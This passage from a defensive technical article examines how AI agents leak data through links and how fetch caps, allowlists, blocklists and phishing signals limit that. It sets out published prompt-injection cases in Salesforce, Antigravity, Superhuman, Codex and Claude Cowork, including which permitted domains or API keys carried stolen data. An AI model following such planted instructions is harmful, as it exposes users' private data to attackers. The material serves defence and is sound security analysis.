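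Whether 26 bits is a small leak depends on the secret. That is enough for only five letters of a customer's name, but a six-digit login code has a million possible values, or about 20 bits, so four fetches could reveal all of it. With a cap of three, the attacker could still narrow the million codes to about 21. Some secrets can be revealed with one bit, such as whether a company has accepted a takeover offer, and only a cap of zero fetches would protect them.

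The formula also shows that limiting fetches is more effective than limiting links. Halving the number of fetches halves the leak, but a defender would have to cut the number of links from 36 to 6 for the same effect. To double the leak per fetch, an attacker would have to square the number of links, from 36 to 1,296. That is feasible, since Rehberger suggests that an attacker could teach the model a vocabulary of thousands of addresses.

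A cap only works if it covers the whole period in which the attacker can collect data. Anthropic's setting, `max_uses`, caps fetches separately for each turn of a conversation. With a cap of 5, a ten-turn conversation could include 50 fetches, which raises the limit on leaked data from 26 bits to about 258. The fetch tool has no default cap, and Managed Agents, a version of Anthropic's platform where the tool is on by default, doesn't offer the setting. An attack that persists in the agent's memory, like Radware's, could also continue across conversations.

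Rehberger proposes two further limits. The harness could keep a copy of each page for a few minutes, so that a repeat visit would not reach the attacker's server, or it could refuse to visit the same address twice in a session. Either way, the attacker would receive at most one request for each link.

Allowing the agent to use each link only once makes little difference for a short secret. Five different links chosen in order from 36 allow 36 × 35 × 34 × 33 × 32 sequences, or about 45 million, which lowers the limit only from 25.8 bits to 25.4. The restriction helps with longer secrets, because ordinary text repeats letters. With 36 links, it keeps the total under 140 bits, or about 27 characters, no matter how many fetches the agent makes. Without the restriction or a cap on fetches, the total has no limit.

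An attacker could get around the restriction with more links, but under OpenAI's rule the crawler would have to record every one of them first. The restriction would give almost no protection under a provenance rule that accepts links from fetched pages, because a site like Paul's can generate new addresses at every step.

Requests may also arrive out of order, which Rehberger noted in 2023 as an obstacle for attackers. If an attacker learned which five different links the agent had opened but not their order, the limit would fall to 18.5 bits, slightly too few to identify a six-digit code. This protection is unreliable because an agent that waits for each page before opening the next reveals the order.

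The formula assumes that the attacker learns only from which links the agent opens and in what order. If the agent can also control when it opens each link, the timing could reveal more.

Anthropic's tool already caches pages by default, although the documentation describes this as a way to improve speed, and developers can turn it off. A stricter design would give the agent the crawler's stored copy of a page and never contact the live site. The attacker's server would receive nothing from the agent, but the agent would sometimes read an outdated page.

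### What the two rules leave open

The rules differ most on links that the agent did not compose but that nobody has published either.

| Address | Anthropic's provenance rule | OpenAI's public-URL rule |
|---|---|---|
| An attacker's address to which the model added private data | Refused | Warning, or a different website |
| A ready-made link on a page that the agent fetched | Refused in the Claude chat app, accepted by default through the API | Loaded only if the crawler has recorded it |
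| A private invoice link in an email | Depends on which tool delivered the email | Warning, or a different website |
| An address that the user typed | Accepted | Accepted, as far as Rehberger can tell |

Agents that do office work often have to open links to invoices, shared documents and parcel deliveries. These links are often unique to one recipient, so a public crawler should not have recorded them. Under OpenAI's rule, the bill-paying agent would have to show the owner a warning, because no other website has the invoice. OpenAI notes that frequent warnings can train people to click through without thinking, so the design of the warning matters.

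Anthropic's rule gives less consistent results. If the developer's own software fetches the mail, the link counts as part of a tool result and Claude can open it. If the mail arrives through an MCP connector, Claude can't open the link with the tool until it appears in an approved source, for example when the owner pastes it into a message. A sender who includes several links can learn something from which one the agent opens, even if the agent doesn't change the address.

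Neither rule checks the page that the agent receives, and planted instructions can do harm without sending any data out. Radware showed this by altering a user's medical history stored in ChatGPT's memory, which led to harmful advice.

The rules also protect only the products and features where the vendor has applied them. ChatGPT's phone and desktop apps lacked the image check, and Deep Research could open addresses that the check would have blocked for images. Rehberger sees this as a continuing risk at OpenAI because developers who build new features may not know the defense exists.

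*The Framing Gap* (2026) tested prompt injections designed to extract a secret. Some versions succeeded in up to 100% of trials against a model reached through the API, but none succeeded in 48 valid trials in the ChatGPT product. The paper doesn't attribute the difference to any particular safeguard, because the product's internal workings weren't observable. Zero successes in 48 trials is also compatible with a true success rate of up to about 6%.

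A company that builds its own agent on an API therefore can't assume that it gets the protections of the vendor's chat app. *The Framing Gap* also tested two defenses that such a company could build itself. Splitting the agent so that the part that reads untrusted text can't act on it reduced the leaks to zero and preserved 90% of the agent's usefulness. A list of permitted destinations also stopped every attack, however the attacker encoded the data, but it blocked legitimate traffic to other sites.

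## Building and enforcing a list of permitted domains

Lists of permitted destinations, or allowlists, have done worse in commercial products than in *The Framing Gap*. Between September 2025 and January 2026, researchers published attacks on products from Salesforce, Google, Superhuman and Anthropic that sent private data out through a domain the vendor had permitted.

### Drawing up a list for one task

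A list is easier to get right for one task than for everything an agent might ever do. The bill-paying agent reads invoices, compares them with the company's records and pays the correct ones. Its list could be this short:

| Host | Access | Why the task needs it | Owner of the entry | Entry expires |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `mail.example.com` | Read | Invoices arrive here | Office manager | June 30, 2027 |
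| `books.example.com` | Read and write | Purchase orders and payment records | Bookkeeper | June 30, 2027 |
| `pay.acorn.example` | Read | Acorn's invoices | Bookkeeper | End of Acorn's contract |
| `transfers.example.org` | Read and write | The company's payment service | Bookkeeper | March 31, 2027 |

The company can find out which sites the task needs by running the agent on a few old invoices and logging every host it contacts. A site that merely seems useful stays off the list until a real invoice requires it. Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome admin controls* similarly advises organizations using the Chrome extension to start with a restrictive list and expand it over time.

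Each entry can cover one host or a group of related hosts, and the syntax varies by product. In Anthropic's fetch tool, `acorn.example` automatically covers every subdomain. In Salesforce's *Manage Trusted URLs*, an administrator writes `*.acorn.example` to cover them. Docker's fetch tool also accepts a leading dot, as in `.acorn.example`, which covers the subdomains but not the domain itself. The narrowest entry that works is the safest, because a wildcard also permits any subdomain that Acorn gives to a contractor or customer, including those it creates later.

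Reading and writing need separate permissions, since the agent has no reason to fill in forms on a site where it only looks things up. Separate permissions don't prevent the agent from leaking data through the URLs it requests, because that requires only read access.

When an entry expires, its owner checks that the task still needs the site and that the same organization still controls the domain. If nobody checks, the harness drops the entry, and the worst result is usually a delayed payment. An entry without an expiry date can stay on the list after the domain's registration lapses, as happened at Salesforce.

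### Domains that anyone could buy or use

Companies keep customer records in Salesforce, whose Agentforce agents read and act on them. A company can put a Web-to-Lead form on its website that lets any visitor create a record by sending an inquiry. In ForcedLeak, an attack that the security company Noma published in September 2025, the inquiry contained instructions. Willison explains that when an employee asked Agentforce about the inquiry, the agent looked up the email addresses of other potential customers and wrote them into an image URL.

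Salesforce's content security policy was meant to stop browsers from loading images from unknown sites. It permitted `my-salesforce-cms.com`, which looks like one of Salesforce's own domains, but the domain's registration had expired. According to BeyondMachines' *Critical flaw in Salesforce Agentforce enables data exfiltration through AI agent exploitation*, the researchers bought it for $5. The policy then allowed browsers to send the data to the researchers' server.

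Google made a mistake in the default list of permitted domains for Antigravity, its code editor. The editor includes a browser that its agent can control, and by default the agent may open only domains on this list. PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* found that the list included `webhook.site`, a service that gives anyone an address and shows them every request sent to it. Developers use such services to test software, which is presumably why Google included it.

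PromptArmor hid instructions in an online guide to connecting two pieces of software. The agent read the guide, collected cloud credentials and samples of the user's code, and opened a `webhook.site` address that contained them. The attack worked only if the user had turned on the browser feature. PromptArmor otherwise used the recommended settings, which let the agent decide when to ask a person for review.

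PromptArmor didn't report the problem privately to Google first, because Google already warned new users about data exfiltration. In November 2025, Willison noted that Google listed data exfiltration through the browser agent as a known issue it was working to fix. Users can open the list of permitted domains from Antigravity's settings, so they don't have to wait for Google to remove the entry.

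### Services that belong to trusted companies

Superhuman's mail assistant permitted images from `docs.google.com`. Google controls that host, but Google Forms runs there, and anyone with a Google account can create a form and read the responses. PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes an attack in which a single answer from the assistant sent partial contents of more than 40 emails to the attacker's form. The user only had to ask for a summary of recent mail and didn't have to open the malicious message.

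Superhuman received the report on a Friday night, disabled the vulnerable features on Monday and released its first patch on Tuesday, December 9, 2025. PromptArmor also found that the assistant's web search could open any address, so an attacker using that feature didn't need Google Forms.

Not all other developers learned from the case. More than three months after the case became public, PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* described the same Google Forms route in OpenAI's Codex, which had expanded from coding into office work. PromptArmor reported the flaw on April 21, 2026, and OpenAI has fixed it.

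Anthropic made the mistake of permitting its own domain. When Claude writes code for a user, the code runs in a sandbox, an isolated environment with limited network access. The default setting, "Package managers only", permitted sites for downloading software. Rehberger found in Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* that, despite its name, the setting also permitted `api.anthropic.com`, the address through which outside software uses Claude.

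The API stores each uploaded file in the account whose key comes with the request. An attacker could therefore include their own key in the planted instructions, and Claude's code would upload the user's files to the attacker's account. One upload could carry 30 MB, or about 240 million bits, compared with roughly 1,200 bits in a single web address.

Rehberger reported this on October 25, 2025. Anthropic closed the report within an hour as out of scope, but acknowledged on October 30 that it should not have. The route still worked when Anthropic released Claude Cowork in January 2026. Two days later, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed hidden instructions in a document causing Cowork to upload a loan estimate without asking for approval. The estimate contained partial social security numbers.

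That demonstration used Claude Haiku, one of Anthropic's smaller models. Opus 4.5, which resists prompt injection better, also uploaded customer records in a separate test, so the gap in the list was exploitable even with a stronger model. TechNadu's *Anthropic Claude Vulnerability Exposes Cowork AI to Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection* reports that Anthropic acknowledged the risk and was updating Cowork's virtual machine (the simulated computer that serves as its sandbox) to restrict file access.

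### Judging a domain by who can receive data there

All four lists contained a domain where a stranger could receive data. The owner's reputation was no help, since Google and Anthropic were in full control of their servers throughout. Before adding a domain, the owner of the entry should ask:

- Has the registration lapsed, or could it lapse before the entry expires?
- Can anyone open an account, create a form or rent storage on this host, and read what arrives?
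- Does the host publish what visitors send, for example as comments?
- Does any service on the host redirect visitors or fetch other addresses on request?

By this test, a supplier's plain website can be safer to list than a Google site, if the supplier is honest and keeps its server secure. Many popular domains fail the test. PromptArmor's *What domains should I add to my allowlist* warns that domains companies commonly list can be used to send data out, and Rehberger thinks that others on Anthropic's package list, which includes GitHub, may allow similar attacks. Willison says it is "tricky" to find domains that can't leak anything.

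An office agent may still need Google Docs or GitHub. If a company can't remove such a domain from the list, it can limit what the agent sends there.

Salesforce recovered the expired domain and then restricted the agent's output. Since September 8, 2025, it has enforced a list called Trusted URLs for Agentforce and its Einstein AI services. PromptArmor's *One key way Salesforce mitigates AI risk* explains that Salesforce's web app replaces every unlisted address in an answer with `[URL_REDACTED]` before displaying it, which prevents the browser from loading outside images and the user from clicking phishing links. Salesforce can also swap names, card numbers and other sensitive details for placeholders before the text reaches the model, so the model can't leak the real values. Redaction doesn't cover actions the agent takes with other tools, which need their own controls.

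An administrator can still undo much of this protection. Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* uses `https://docs.google.com` as its example of an address to add, the same host Superhuman had permitted. According to an older version of Salesforce's Trusted URLs guide, each new entry also allows images by default. A company that followed both pages could reopen the route through Google Forms. PromptArmor advises turning images off for each entry that doesn't need them and avoiding wildcards for sites that host users' content.

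For Anthropic's API, Rehberger suggested that the sandbox should let Claude communicate only with the logged-in user's account. A filter that checks only the host can't enforce this, because every account uses the same host. One solution is to route requests through a proxy outside the sandbox. The proxy discards any API key that the agent's code supplies and adds the user's own. A stolen file would then end up in the user's account, where the attacker can't read it. The same approach works for cloud storage and other services where strangers can have accounts, as long as the proxy can read the decrypted request.

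### Where to enforce the list

The harness can apply a list of permitted domains in its fetch tool, the app can apply one through the browser's content security policy, and a firewall or proxy can apply one where traffic leaves the agent's environment.

| Enforcement point | Traffic it covers | What it can check | What it misses |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fetch tool | Requests made with that tool | The full address and where it came from | Code the agent runs, and images in its answers |
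| Content security policy | Content that the browser loads into the app's page | Mainly the host and the type of content | Background fetches, and messages displayed in other apps |
| Network boundary | Everything that leaves the agent's environment | Usually only the host | The user's own browser, and whose account receives the data |

A rule on one tool does not restrict other tools that can reach the network, so Cowork has two controls. Anthropic explains that web fetches run directly on the user's device, under a permission system that applies the organization's network settings. Code runs in a virtual machine, which has its own network filter.

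A content security policy applies only to the page that sets it. Willison describes a May 2026 case in which Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could send email to the user's own inbox without approval. The emails could contain images from outside sites, so opening one could leak data, including OneDrive links that let anyone who had them download the user's files.

Enforcing the list at the network boundary is a good backstop because it also covers tools that developers add later. GitHub's *Network Permissions* describes a firewall for automated agent workflows that works with Copilot, Claude, Codex and Gemini. Developers can write a list for each workflow, and without one the agent can reach only basic infrastructure such as common software sources. For an analysis sandbox where Claude runs code, Anthropic groups the permitted domains by purpose, and users can switch off every group except the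 one for installing software.

The fetch tool is the better place for finer rules. For example, if developers set it up to send a password or key with each request, Docker advises them to limit the tool to the hosts that should receive that credential. A company can combine a broad list at the boundary with a narrower one in each tool.

### Company-wide lists in Edge and Claude

Microsoft's agent for its Edge browser has no permitted sites by default and stays unavailable until an administrator lists some, according to Microsoft's *Configure browsing with Copilot*. The feature is still in preview and available only to organizations outside the European Economic Area. Copilot also asks the user to take over for logins and for final steps such as saving or submitting.

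An administrator can switch on a ready-made list of sites that people commonly use for work, then block individual sites on it. Blocked sites take precedence over allowed ones. Antigravity's default list is a good reason to check each entry before switching on such a list. Microsoft's *Browsing with Copilot Blocked URLs* also lets the administrator allow every site by entering a single asterisk, then block exceptions. That turns the allowlist into a blocklist, which would allow an attacker's new domain.

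The consumer version of Edge also starts with a curated list, but its users can approve more sites, according to the guide *Allow or Block Sites for Browse with Copilot in Microsoft Edge*.

Anthropic offers separate controls for developers and organizations. A developer using the fetch tool can set either `allowed_domains` or `blocked_domains`, but not both in the same request. An entry can include a path, such as `example.com/blog`. Anthropic recommends using plain Latin characters in entries to guard against lookalike domains.

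An organization can have both an allowlist and a blocklist for Claude in Chrome, and the same lists apply to the browser built into Cowork. The lists restrict only Claude. If an employee types a blocked address into the built-in browser, the page still loads with a warning banner, but Claude's tools stay off.

### Lists that change with the task

A company-wide list has to include every site that any task might need, so an agent that is paying Acorn could also reach the payroll service, the customer database and everything else on the list. A separate list for each task removes that access, but administrators can't predict all the tasks people will give browser agents, so software has to write the list as the task proceeds.

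Parker (2025), in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*, describes Google's design, called Agent Origin Sets. It works as follows:

1. The model planning the task proposes an origin (scheme, host and port).
2. A gating function decides whether the origin is relevant to what the user asked for. This function doesn't see any web content, so a malicious page can't address it directly.
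3. Chrome adds the origin to one of two sets for that session. The agent can read from both sets, but it can click and type only on origins in the read-writable set.
4. Chrome withholds everything else from the model, including advertisements and other frames from unrelated sites within a permitted page.

If a user asks the agent to order ingredients for a recipe, the recipe site would be read-only and the grocery store's site read-writable. Instructions hidden in the recipe couldn't make the agent type into the user's mail, because the mail site would be in neither set. Chrome also restricts URLs that the model generates to known, public ones, much as OpenAI's public-URL rule does.

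Before the agent can visit a new site, a second model must approve it. An attacker might still get a site approved by making it look relevant to the task. Google pays up to $20,000 to researchers who demonstrate breaches of these boundaries.

As of December 2025, Google had built only a simpler version that tracked the read-writable set. Shortly afterward, *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy* (Roesner and Kohlbrenner, 2026) tested seven browsers with agents. In the attack it describes, a malicious page embeds a page from another site, such as the user's bank, which browsers normally prevent it from reading. When the user asks for a summary, planted instructions make the agent copy the embedded content into the attacker's form.

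The attack worked in full on ChatGPT Atlas. The researchers found that Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome and Perplexity's Comet met the necessary conditions for the attack, provided a prompt injection succeeded. Chrome's result may reflect the missing read-only set, because the agent would have had nothing to copy if the browser had withheld unrelated frames. The researchers ran the tests in January and February, and the products may have changed since.

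In the mode that Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome permissions guide* calls "Manually approve", Claude proposes a plan that names the websites it will use for a task. Once the user approves the plan, Claude can work on those sites but must ask before using any other. The user can also give Claude permanent permission to act on a site by choosing "Always allow actions on this site", but Claude still asks before it downloads a file or enters potentially sensitive information.

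The Cowork side panel defaults to "Automatically approve" mode, in which Claude checks the safety of each action and pauses only when it needs approval. An organization that relies on this mode should also have its own list of permitted domains, because Claude's checks depend on the model's judgment.

### Where strict lists fit best

Strict lists work badly when nobody can name the necessary sites in advance. A research agent limited to listed domains would miss most of what a search turns up. Business software has a milder version of the problem. TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI* reported that when Salesforce began enforcing Trusted URLs, administrators had to add every outside domain their agents used or risk disruption.

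Roesner and Kohlbrenner found a similar trade-off among browsers. Brave, Edge and Firefox had stronger security but more limited agents, while the more capable agents could do nearly anything a user could.

Frequent refusals can also weaken the list, because users who are repeatedly interrupted may start approving sites without checking them or ask the administrator for a wildcard. Parker expects Google to adjust its gating to reduce unnecessary friction.

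Some products let administrators log unlisted addresses for review without removing them from answers. Glean's *Untrusted URL monitoring* describes this option for an assistant that searches company data. Administrators can use the log to see which sites people need before blocking any. But the answer reaches the user unchanged, so if it contains an image whose address carries private data, displaying the image could leak that data before anyone reads the log.

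A strict list is most justified for repetitive tasks that involve sensitive data and a stable set of sites, such as paying bills, updating customer records or building software automatically. Anthropic's *Use Claude in Chrome safely* recommends a restrictive allowlist to organizations that handle sensitive data. If an organization has turned on Anthropic's settings for HIPAA, the US health privacy law, Claude in Chrome can't open any site until an account owner permits specific sites or changes the default policy.

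A company that needs both kinds of work can use two agents. One researches suppliers on the open web and has no access to mail or accounts. The other pays the bills and can reach only the four hosts on its list. The bookkeeper adds a host when the company signs up a new supplier, which happens much less often than receiving an invoice.

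## Using blocklists and other reputation signals

A research agent has to visit sites nobody listed in advance, but its harness can still check whether anyone has identified an address as harmful. A blocklist blocks destinations listed as harmful and allows all others. The best known is Google Safe Browsing, which according to Google helps protect more than five billion devices.

### How Safe Browsing works

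Before adding a phishing page to a blocklist, the operator has to discover the address, for example through a report or a spam filter, and confirm that the page is harmful. According to *PhishTime* (Oest, Safaei and colleagues, 2020), operators verify pages because a false alarm would disrupt an honest site. In *Safe Browsing site status*, Google says it examines billions of addresses and finds thousands of new unsafe sites each day. Many of those are legitimate sites that an attacker has broken into.

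Google's *Real Time Mode* sets out how software checks an address. Slightly simplified, the steps are:

1. The software splits the address into combinations of host and path, so that one entry can cover a single page or a whole site. For `pay.acorn.example/4471`, the combinations include the full address and `acorn.example/`.
2. It computes a hash of each combination, which is a fixed-length code derived from the text.
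3. It looks for the hashes in a stored file of sites that are probably harmless. If it finds one, it checks only a local copy of the threat lists and skips the remaining steps.
4. Otherwise, it sends Google the first four bytes of each hash.
5. Google returns the full hash of every listed threat that starts with those bytes. The software compares them with its own hashes and reports UNSAFE if any match and SAFE if none do.

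Sending only four bytes protects the user's privacy because there are about 4.3 billion possible four-byte values, so many addresses share each one. An agent needs this protection too, since the addresses it opens may contain private data, and a harness that sent full addresses to a checking service would create another leak.

SAFE means only that Google had no matching entry. A third result, UNSURE, covers network errors and the sites in the stored file, and in those cases the software falls back on its local lists. Google's *No Storage Real Time Mode* describes a simpler version without a local database, which may suit a small harness. The Safe Browsing API is limited to non-commercial use, according to Google's description as reproduced by Deno, so developers of commercial agents need the paid equivalent, Google Cloud's *Web Risk*, which uses the same technology.

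### How much phishing the lists catch

Blocklists lag behind attackers, because a page usually has to be online before anyone can list it. *Sunrise to Sunset* (Oest, Zhang and colleagues, 2020) measured the delay using visits to phishing pages that impersonated one large financial company. The average attack lasted 21 hours from the first victim's visit to the last. Anti-phishing organizations detected it about nine hours after the first visit, and browser warnings took another seven hours to peak.

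PhishTime tested blocklists by building 2,862 harmless imitations of phishing sites and reporting them directly to the blocklists. The average delay was as short as 55 minutes for plain sites and as long as 2 hours 58 minutes for sites that used common evasion techniques. These times are much shorter than the nine hours in the other study, which suggests that much of the usual delay comes from discovering a site.

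*7 Days Later* (Lee, Lim and colleagues, 2025) is the largest recent study of how long phishing sites last. Over five months, the researchers collected 286,237 phishing addresses from the Anti-Phishing Working Group (APWG), which pools reports from banks, security companies and internet providers. Their crawler visited each address every 30 minutes until the page failed to load three times in a row. Half the sites disappeared within 5.46 hours, but some lasted for weeks, which raised the average to 54 hours.

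Safe Browsing flagged only 18.4% of the addresses. The median delay was 5.8 hours, but a minority of slow detections raised the average to 4.5 days. In 84% of the detections, the site had already gone offline. Of the seven other blocklists in the study, OpenPhish did best, but it contained less than 6% of the addresses.

The 18.4% figure depends strongly on the choice of sample. Every address had already reached the APWG, but Google isn't a member and, according to the researchers, has no access to APWG data. The figure therefore measures the overlap between two collections built by different organizations. Safe Browsing's list contained about 10 million entries during the study, and a sample drawn from Google's discoveries would have given a much higher rate. A sample that included unreported phishing might have given a lower one.

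The researchers also downloaded Safe Browsing's list through an older interface, so the result doesn't include Chrome's newer real-time checks. They counted addresses rather than visits, so 18.4% isn't the share of phishing attempts that Chrome stops.

Google's own figures don't settle that question. In March 2024, Google announced real-time checks for all Chrome users with standard protection, because most unsafe sites existed for less than ten minutes and Chrome updated its local list only every 30 to 60 minutes (Google, 2024). 9to5Google reported that Google expected the change to block 25% more phishing attempts. Lee and colleagues' crawler would have missed most sites that lasted less than ten minutes, since it started only after a report and returned every half hour. The public charts in Google's *Transparency Report* were last updated on September 30, 2023. They count the warnings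 that users saw and don't measure the attacks that Safe Browsing missed.

A newer study, *ReDence* (Kaur, Horáček and colleagues, 2026), tested Chrome itself with its strongest protection setting turned on. The researchers used an AI investigator to examine sites that appeared in a public stream of new security certificates in October 2026, and confirmed 4,042 scams by hand. Chrome flagged 16.3% of them at first and 33.0% within seven days. The researchers had reported every site to Google, which may have raised the later figure.

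Chrome initially flagged 44.1% of the sites that stole passwords, but only 7.9% of the other scams, such as fake shops and investment schemes. Fake invoices and supplier bills are the most relevant category for the bill-paying agent. Chrome flagged 21.5% of those 205 sites at first and 44.9% within a week. Combining lists helped only a little. Chrome, Microsoft's SmartScreen and two popular browser extensions together caught 27.5% of all the scams at first.

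### The risk of an unlisted link

Suppose 1 in 1,000 of the links an agent encounters is phishing, and a blocklist catches 18.4% of those without flagging any legitimate links. Out of a million links, 1,000 are phishing and the list catches 184. The other 816 are among the 999,816 unlisted links, so the chance that an unlisted link is phishing is 816 / 999,816, or about 0.082%, compared with 0.100% before the check.

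More generally, if p is the share of links that are phishing and c is the share of phishing that the list catches:

risk of an unlisted link = p(1 − c) / (1 − pc)

The risk falls even less at the moment of the click, because the list may not include the address yet. In Lee and colleagues' sample, only 16% of the flagged sites were still online when Safe Browsing flagged them, and these made up about 3% of all the addresses. An agent that opened each address once while the site was up would have received a warning for at most 3% of them, which lowers the risk only to 0.097%.

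The 3% figure is rough and hard to reconcile with the study's medians of 5.8 hours for detection and 7.9 hours for the lifespan of a flagged site. Sites that stay online for days may also attract more clicks, and Safe Browsing has more time to catch them.

| Share of phishing caught | Source of the figure | Risk of an unlisted link |
|---|---|---|
| 3.0% | Lee and colleagues, flagged while online | 0.097% |
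| 16.3% | Kaur and colleagues, all scams at first | 0.084% |
| 18.4% | Lee and colleagues, flagged at any time | 0.082% |
| 33.0% | Kaur and colleagues, all scams within seven days | 0.067% |
| 44.1% | Kaur and colleagues, password theft at first | 0.056% |

A match is much more informative. If the list wrongly flagged 1 honest link in 100,000, the million links would produce about 10 false alarms and 184 correct matches, so a match would be right 95% of the time. If it wrongly flagged 1 in 1,000, a match would be right only 16% of the time. Operators therefore have good reason to list only pages they have confirmed, even if they miss some phishing.

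### Cloaking

Some phishing sites avoid being confirmed as phishing by cloaking, which means showing scanners a harmless page or an error message while showing targets the phishing page. According to *A Whole New World* (2025), a site can recognize a scanner by the name its software declares, by its IP address, or by whether it runs JavaScript. In *PhishFarm*, Oest, Safaei and colleagues tested simple cloaking on 2,380 harmless imitation phishing sites and found that it made blocklisting over 55% less likely on average.

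Checking a link with more scanners helps, but some phishing addresses get past all of them. *PhishLumos* (2025) describes a system that found 77,391 new addresses by tracing cloaked phishing campaigns. The researchers checked results from roughly 90 security engines, and nearly 20% of the addresses had not been flagged by any of them. The rest counted as detected, which required a flag from only one engine.

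A site can use the same techniques to single out AI agents, as the invented coffee shop in the Memory Heist did. Reputation systems are especially likely to miss such a page because their scanners, and any person who visits to investigate, may receive the harmless version. A victim of ordinary phishing sees the harmful page and can report it, but here the user sees only the agent's answer.

In *Agent-Targeted Cloaking on the Web*, Chen, Chen and Karray (2026) measured how often popular sites treat agents differently. In October 2026, they fetched the same pages as an ordinary browser and as a program that identified itself as ChatGPT's agent. Of 4,705 sites, 21% refused the agent and about 5% gave it different content. Most of the differences weren't specific to AI. For example, some sites gave a simpler version of the page to any visitor that wasn't a browser.

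Only four sites had text that was addressed to AI systems and not sent to browsers. Three served material related to technical documentation. The fourth, a major news publisher, gave AI agents a bank's sponsored copy that human readers never saw. Since the study covered mainly popular sites, it doesn't show how often criminals use the technique.

Chen and colleagues suggest that services that answer questions from web pages should also fetch each page as a browser and flag any text that appears only in the agent's copy. The comparison has to allow for ordinary changes such as rotating headlines, because a simple version flagged 7.2% of sites by chance. If both requests come from the same network, the comparison can also miss a site that recognizes the agent's IP address.

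### Domain age, registrars and certificates

If an address isn't on any list, the harness can still check its domain, starting with its age, because attackers often register domains for a single campaign. *PhiShark2026* (Çolhak, Demirkıran and colleagues, 2026) compared 33,387 scans of phishing pages with 34,115 scans of apparently legitimate ones. Among independently registered domains with a known creation date, 21.0% of the phishing domains were no more than a week old, while 91.5% of the legitimate domains were over five years old.

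The real difference is probably smaller, because the researchers drew the honest sites from a list of the top 10 million domains. The list is ranked largely by links from other sites, so a new business is unlikely to be on it. Refusing every domain up to a week old would have caught only about 12% of the phishing scans. Free hosting services accounted for 45% of the phishing scans, and a page on such a service has the domain age of its host.

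Such a rule would also block honest new sites. In October, Kaur and colleagues' system examined 552,809 working sites from the certificate stream, so refusing all of them would have blocked about 136 other sites for every confirmed scam. Not all of these domains were new, since established sites renew their certificates too. But if Acorn had launched its website that week, the rule would have blocked its invoices.

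An old domain isn't necessarily safe, either. In *Registration, Detection, and Deregistration*, Lim, Mok and colleagues (2025) studied 690,502 phishing domains over 39 months and concluded that attackers had registered 66.1% of them. The rest were legitimate domains that attackers had compromised. On such domains, a long history makes a phishing page look more trustworthy than it is. Blocklists took a median of 86 days to detect the compromised domains, versus 16.3 days for those registered by attackers.

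Registrars, the companies that sell domain names, differ widely in how much abuse they attract. *INFERMAL* (Nosyk, Korczyński and colleagues, 2025) found that each dollar off the price was associated with 49% more malicious domains. Registrars that let software register domains or create accounts had 401% more, while strict registration requirements were associated with 63% fewer. These figures can help registrars prevent abuse, but they are less useful for judging a single domain, since honest buyers like discounts too. In the paper's model of individual domains, registration restrictions lowered the likelihood that a domain was malicious by only about 19%.

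A short certificate lifetime is a weaker sign of phishing than it first appears, because it may indicate only that a site is small. In the PhiShark2026 data, 92.8% of the certificates on independently registered phishing domains were valid for 91 days or less, compared with 61.3% on legitimate domains. But *TLS Certificate and Domain Feature Analysis of Phishing Domains* (2026) separated popular from unpopular legitimate domains under Denmark's `.dk` ending. About 94% of the phishing certificates had lifetimes in the same range, compared with 95% of those for unpopular legitimate domains and 76% for popular ones.

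One of the stronger signals is whether a domain has a DNS record for receiving email. Çolhak and colleagues found one for 86.7% of the honest domains but only 29.7% of the phishing domains. If those rates applied to all links and 1 in 1,000 was phishing, a missing mail record would raise the risk from 0.1% to about 0.5%. That is a reason to look more closely at an invoice, but if a harness refused every link without a mail record, about 199 of every 200 links it refused would be honest.

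### Popular hosts

Popularity rankings such as Tranco order domains by how widely people use them. A high rank makes it unlikely that a criminal owns the domain, but it is weak evidence that pages users publish there, as on `github.io`, are safe. Lim and colleagues used the Tranco ranking to remove such platforms from their data. Their example is `blogspot.com`, where an attacker can create a subdomain that impersonates the US Postal Service.

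Çolhak and colleagues similarly ignored registration and network data for pages on free hosting services but kept what they could observe about the page itself. A harness can do the same by treating age and popularity as unknown on any site where users publish their own pages. Rank is more useful for checking a claim of identity. If a link supposedly leads to a national bank but its domain isn't in the ranking, there is good reason to be suspicious.

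### Acting on the result

A blocklist match is a strong reason to refuse a page, and the harness should do so before any text from the page reaches the model. The harness should also check each step of a redirect chain, because Lee and colleagues found that Safe Browsing was about eight times less likely to flag phishing addresses that used redirects. False alarms happen, so a person should be able to review a refusal, but the agent shouldn't be able to override it.

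A site's absence from a blocklist is only weak evidence that it is safe, so the other checks should still apply in full. The harness should record the result as "not listed" and avoid passing Google's word SAFE to the model, which might treat it as an endorsement. The harness should also check again just before the agent submits anything, because a site that wasn't listed when the agent opened an invoice in the morning may be listed by the time the agent is ready to pay.

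## Asking the model whether a link is safe

After a link has passed every list check, the agent can ask its model whether the link looks safe. The model can judge the address alone, the message that contains it, or other evidence such as the domain's registration record, customer reviews and the text of the page. Error rates differ widely between these tasks, and in each one an attacker controls some of what the model reads.

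### The address alone

*Benchmarking Large Language Models for Zero-shot and Few-shot Phishing URL Detection* (Hasan and BusiReddyGari, 2026) tested GPT-4o, Claude 3.7 Sonnet and Grok 3 Beta on 10,000 web addresses, half of them phishing. The models classified 87.5% to 89.1% correctly from the address alone. Adding six labelled examples to the prompt raised accuracy to between 90.5% and 94%.

An agent meets far fewer phishing links than that, so false alarms matter more than these figures suggest. The researchers also tested the models on samples of 1,000 addresses, of which only 10 were phishing. The published rates for one sample imply that Claude 3.7 Sonnet caught nine of the ten but also flagged 118 legitimate addresses. Grok 3 Beta caught nine with 35 false alarms, so about four out of five of its warnings were wrong.

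Attackers can also write addresses that make a malicious site look safe to a model. *MalURLBench* (Kong, Wu and colleagues, 2026) took the addresses of real malicious sites and added text that made them seem safe to the parts a site's owner can fill in freely: the subdomain, the path and the query. This produced 61,845 addresses for ten everyday situations, such as tracking a parcel or looking for a job. Although the prompt warned of possible attacks, the 12 models tested accepted between 32.9% and 99.9% of the addresses they were given.

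GPT-3.5 Turbo had the lowest acceptance rate, at first only about 14%. Acceptance more than doubled after another model rewrote the addresses that had mostly failed, which a real attacker can also do. GPT-4o ended up accepting about 38%, and the smaller GPT-4o mini about 90%.

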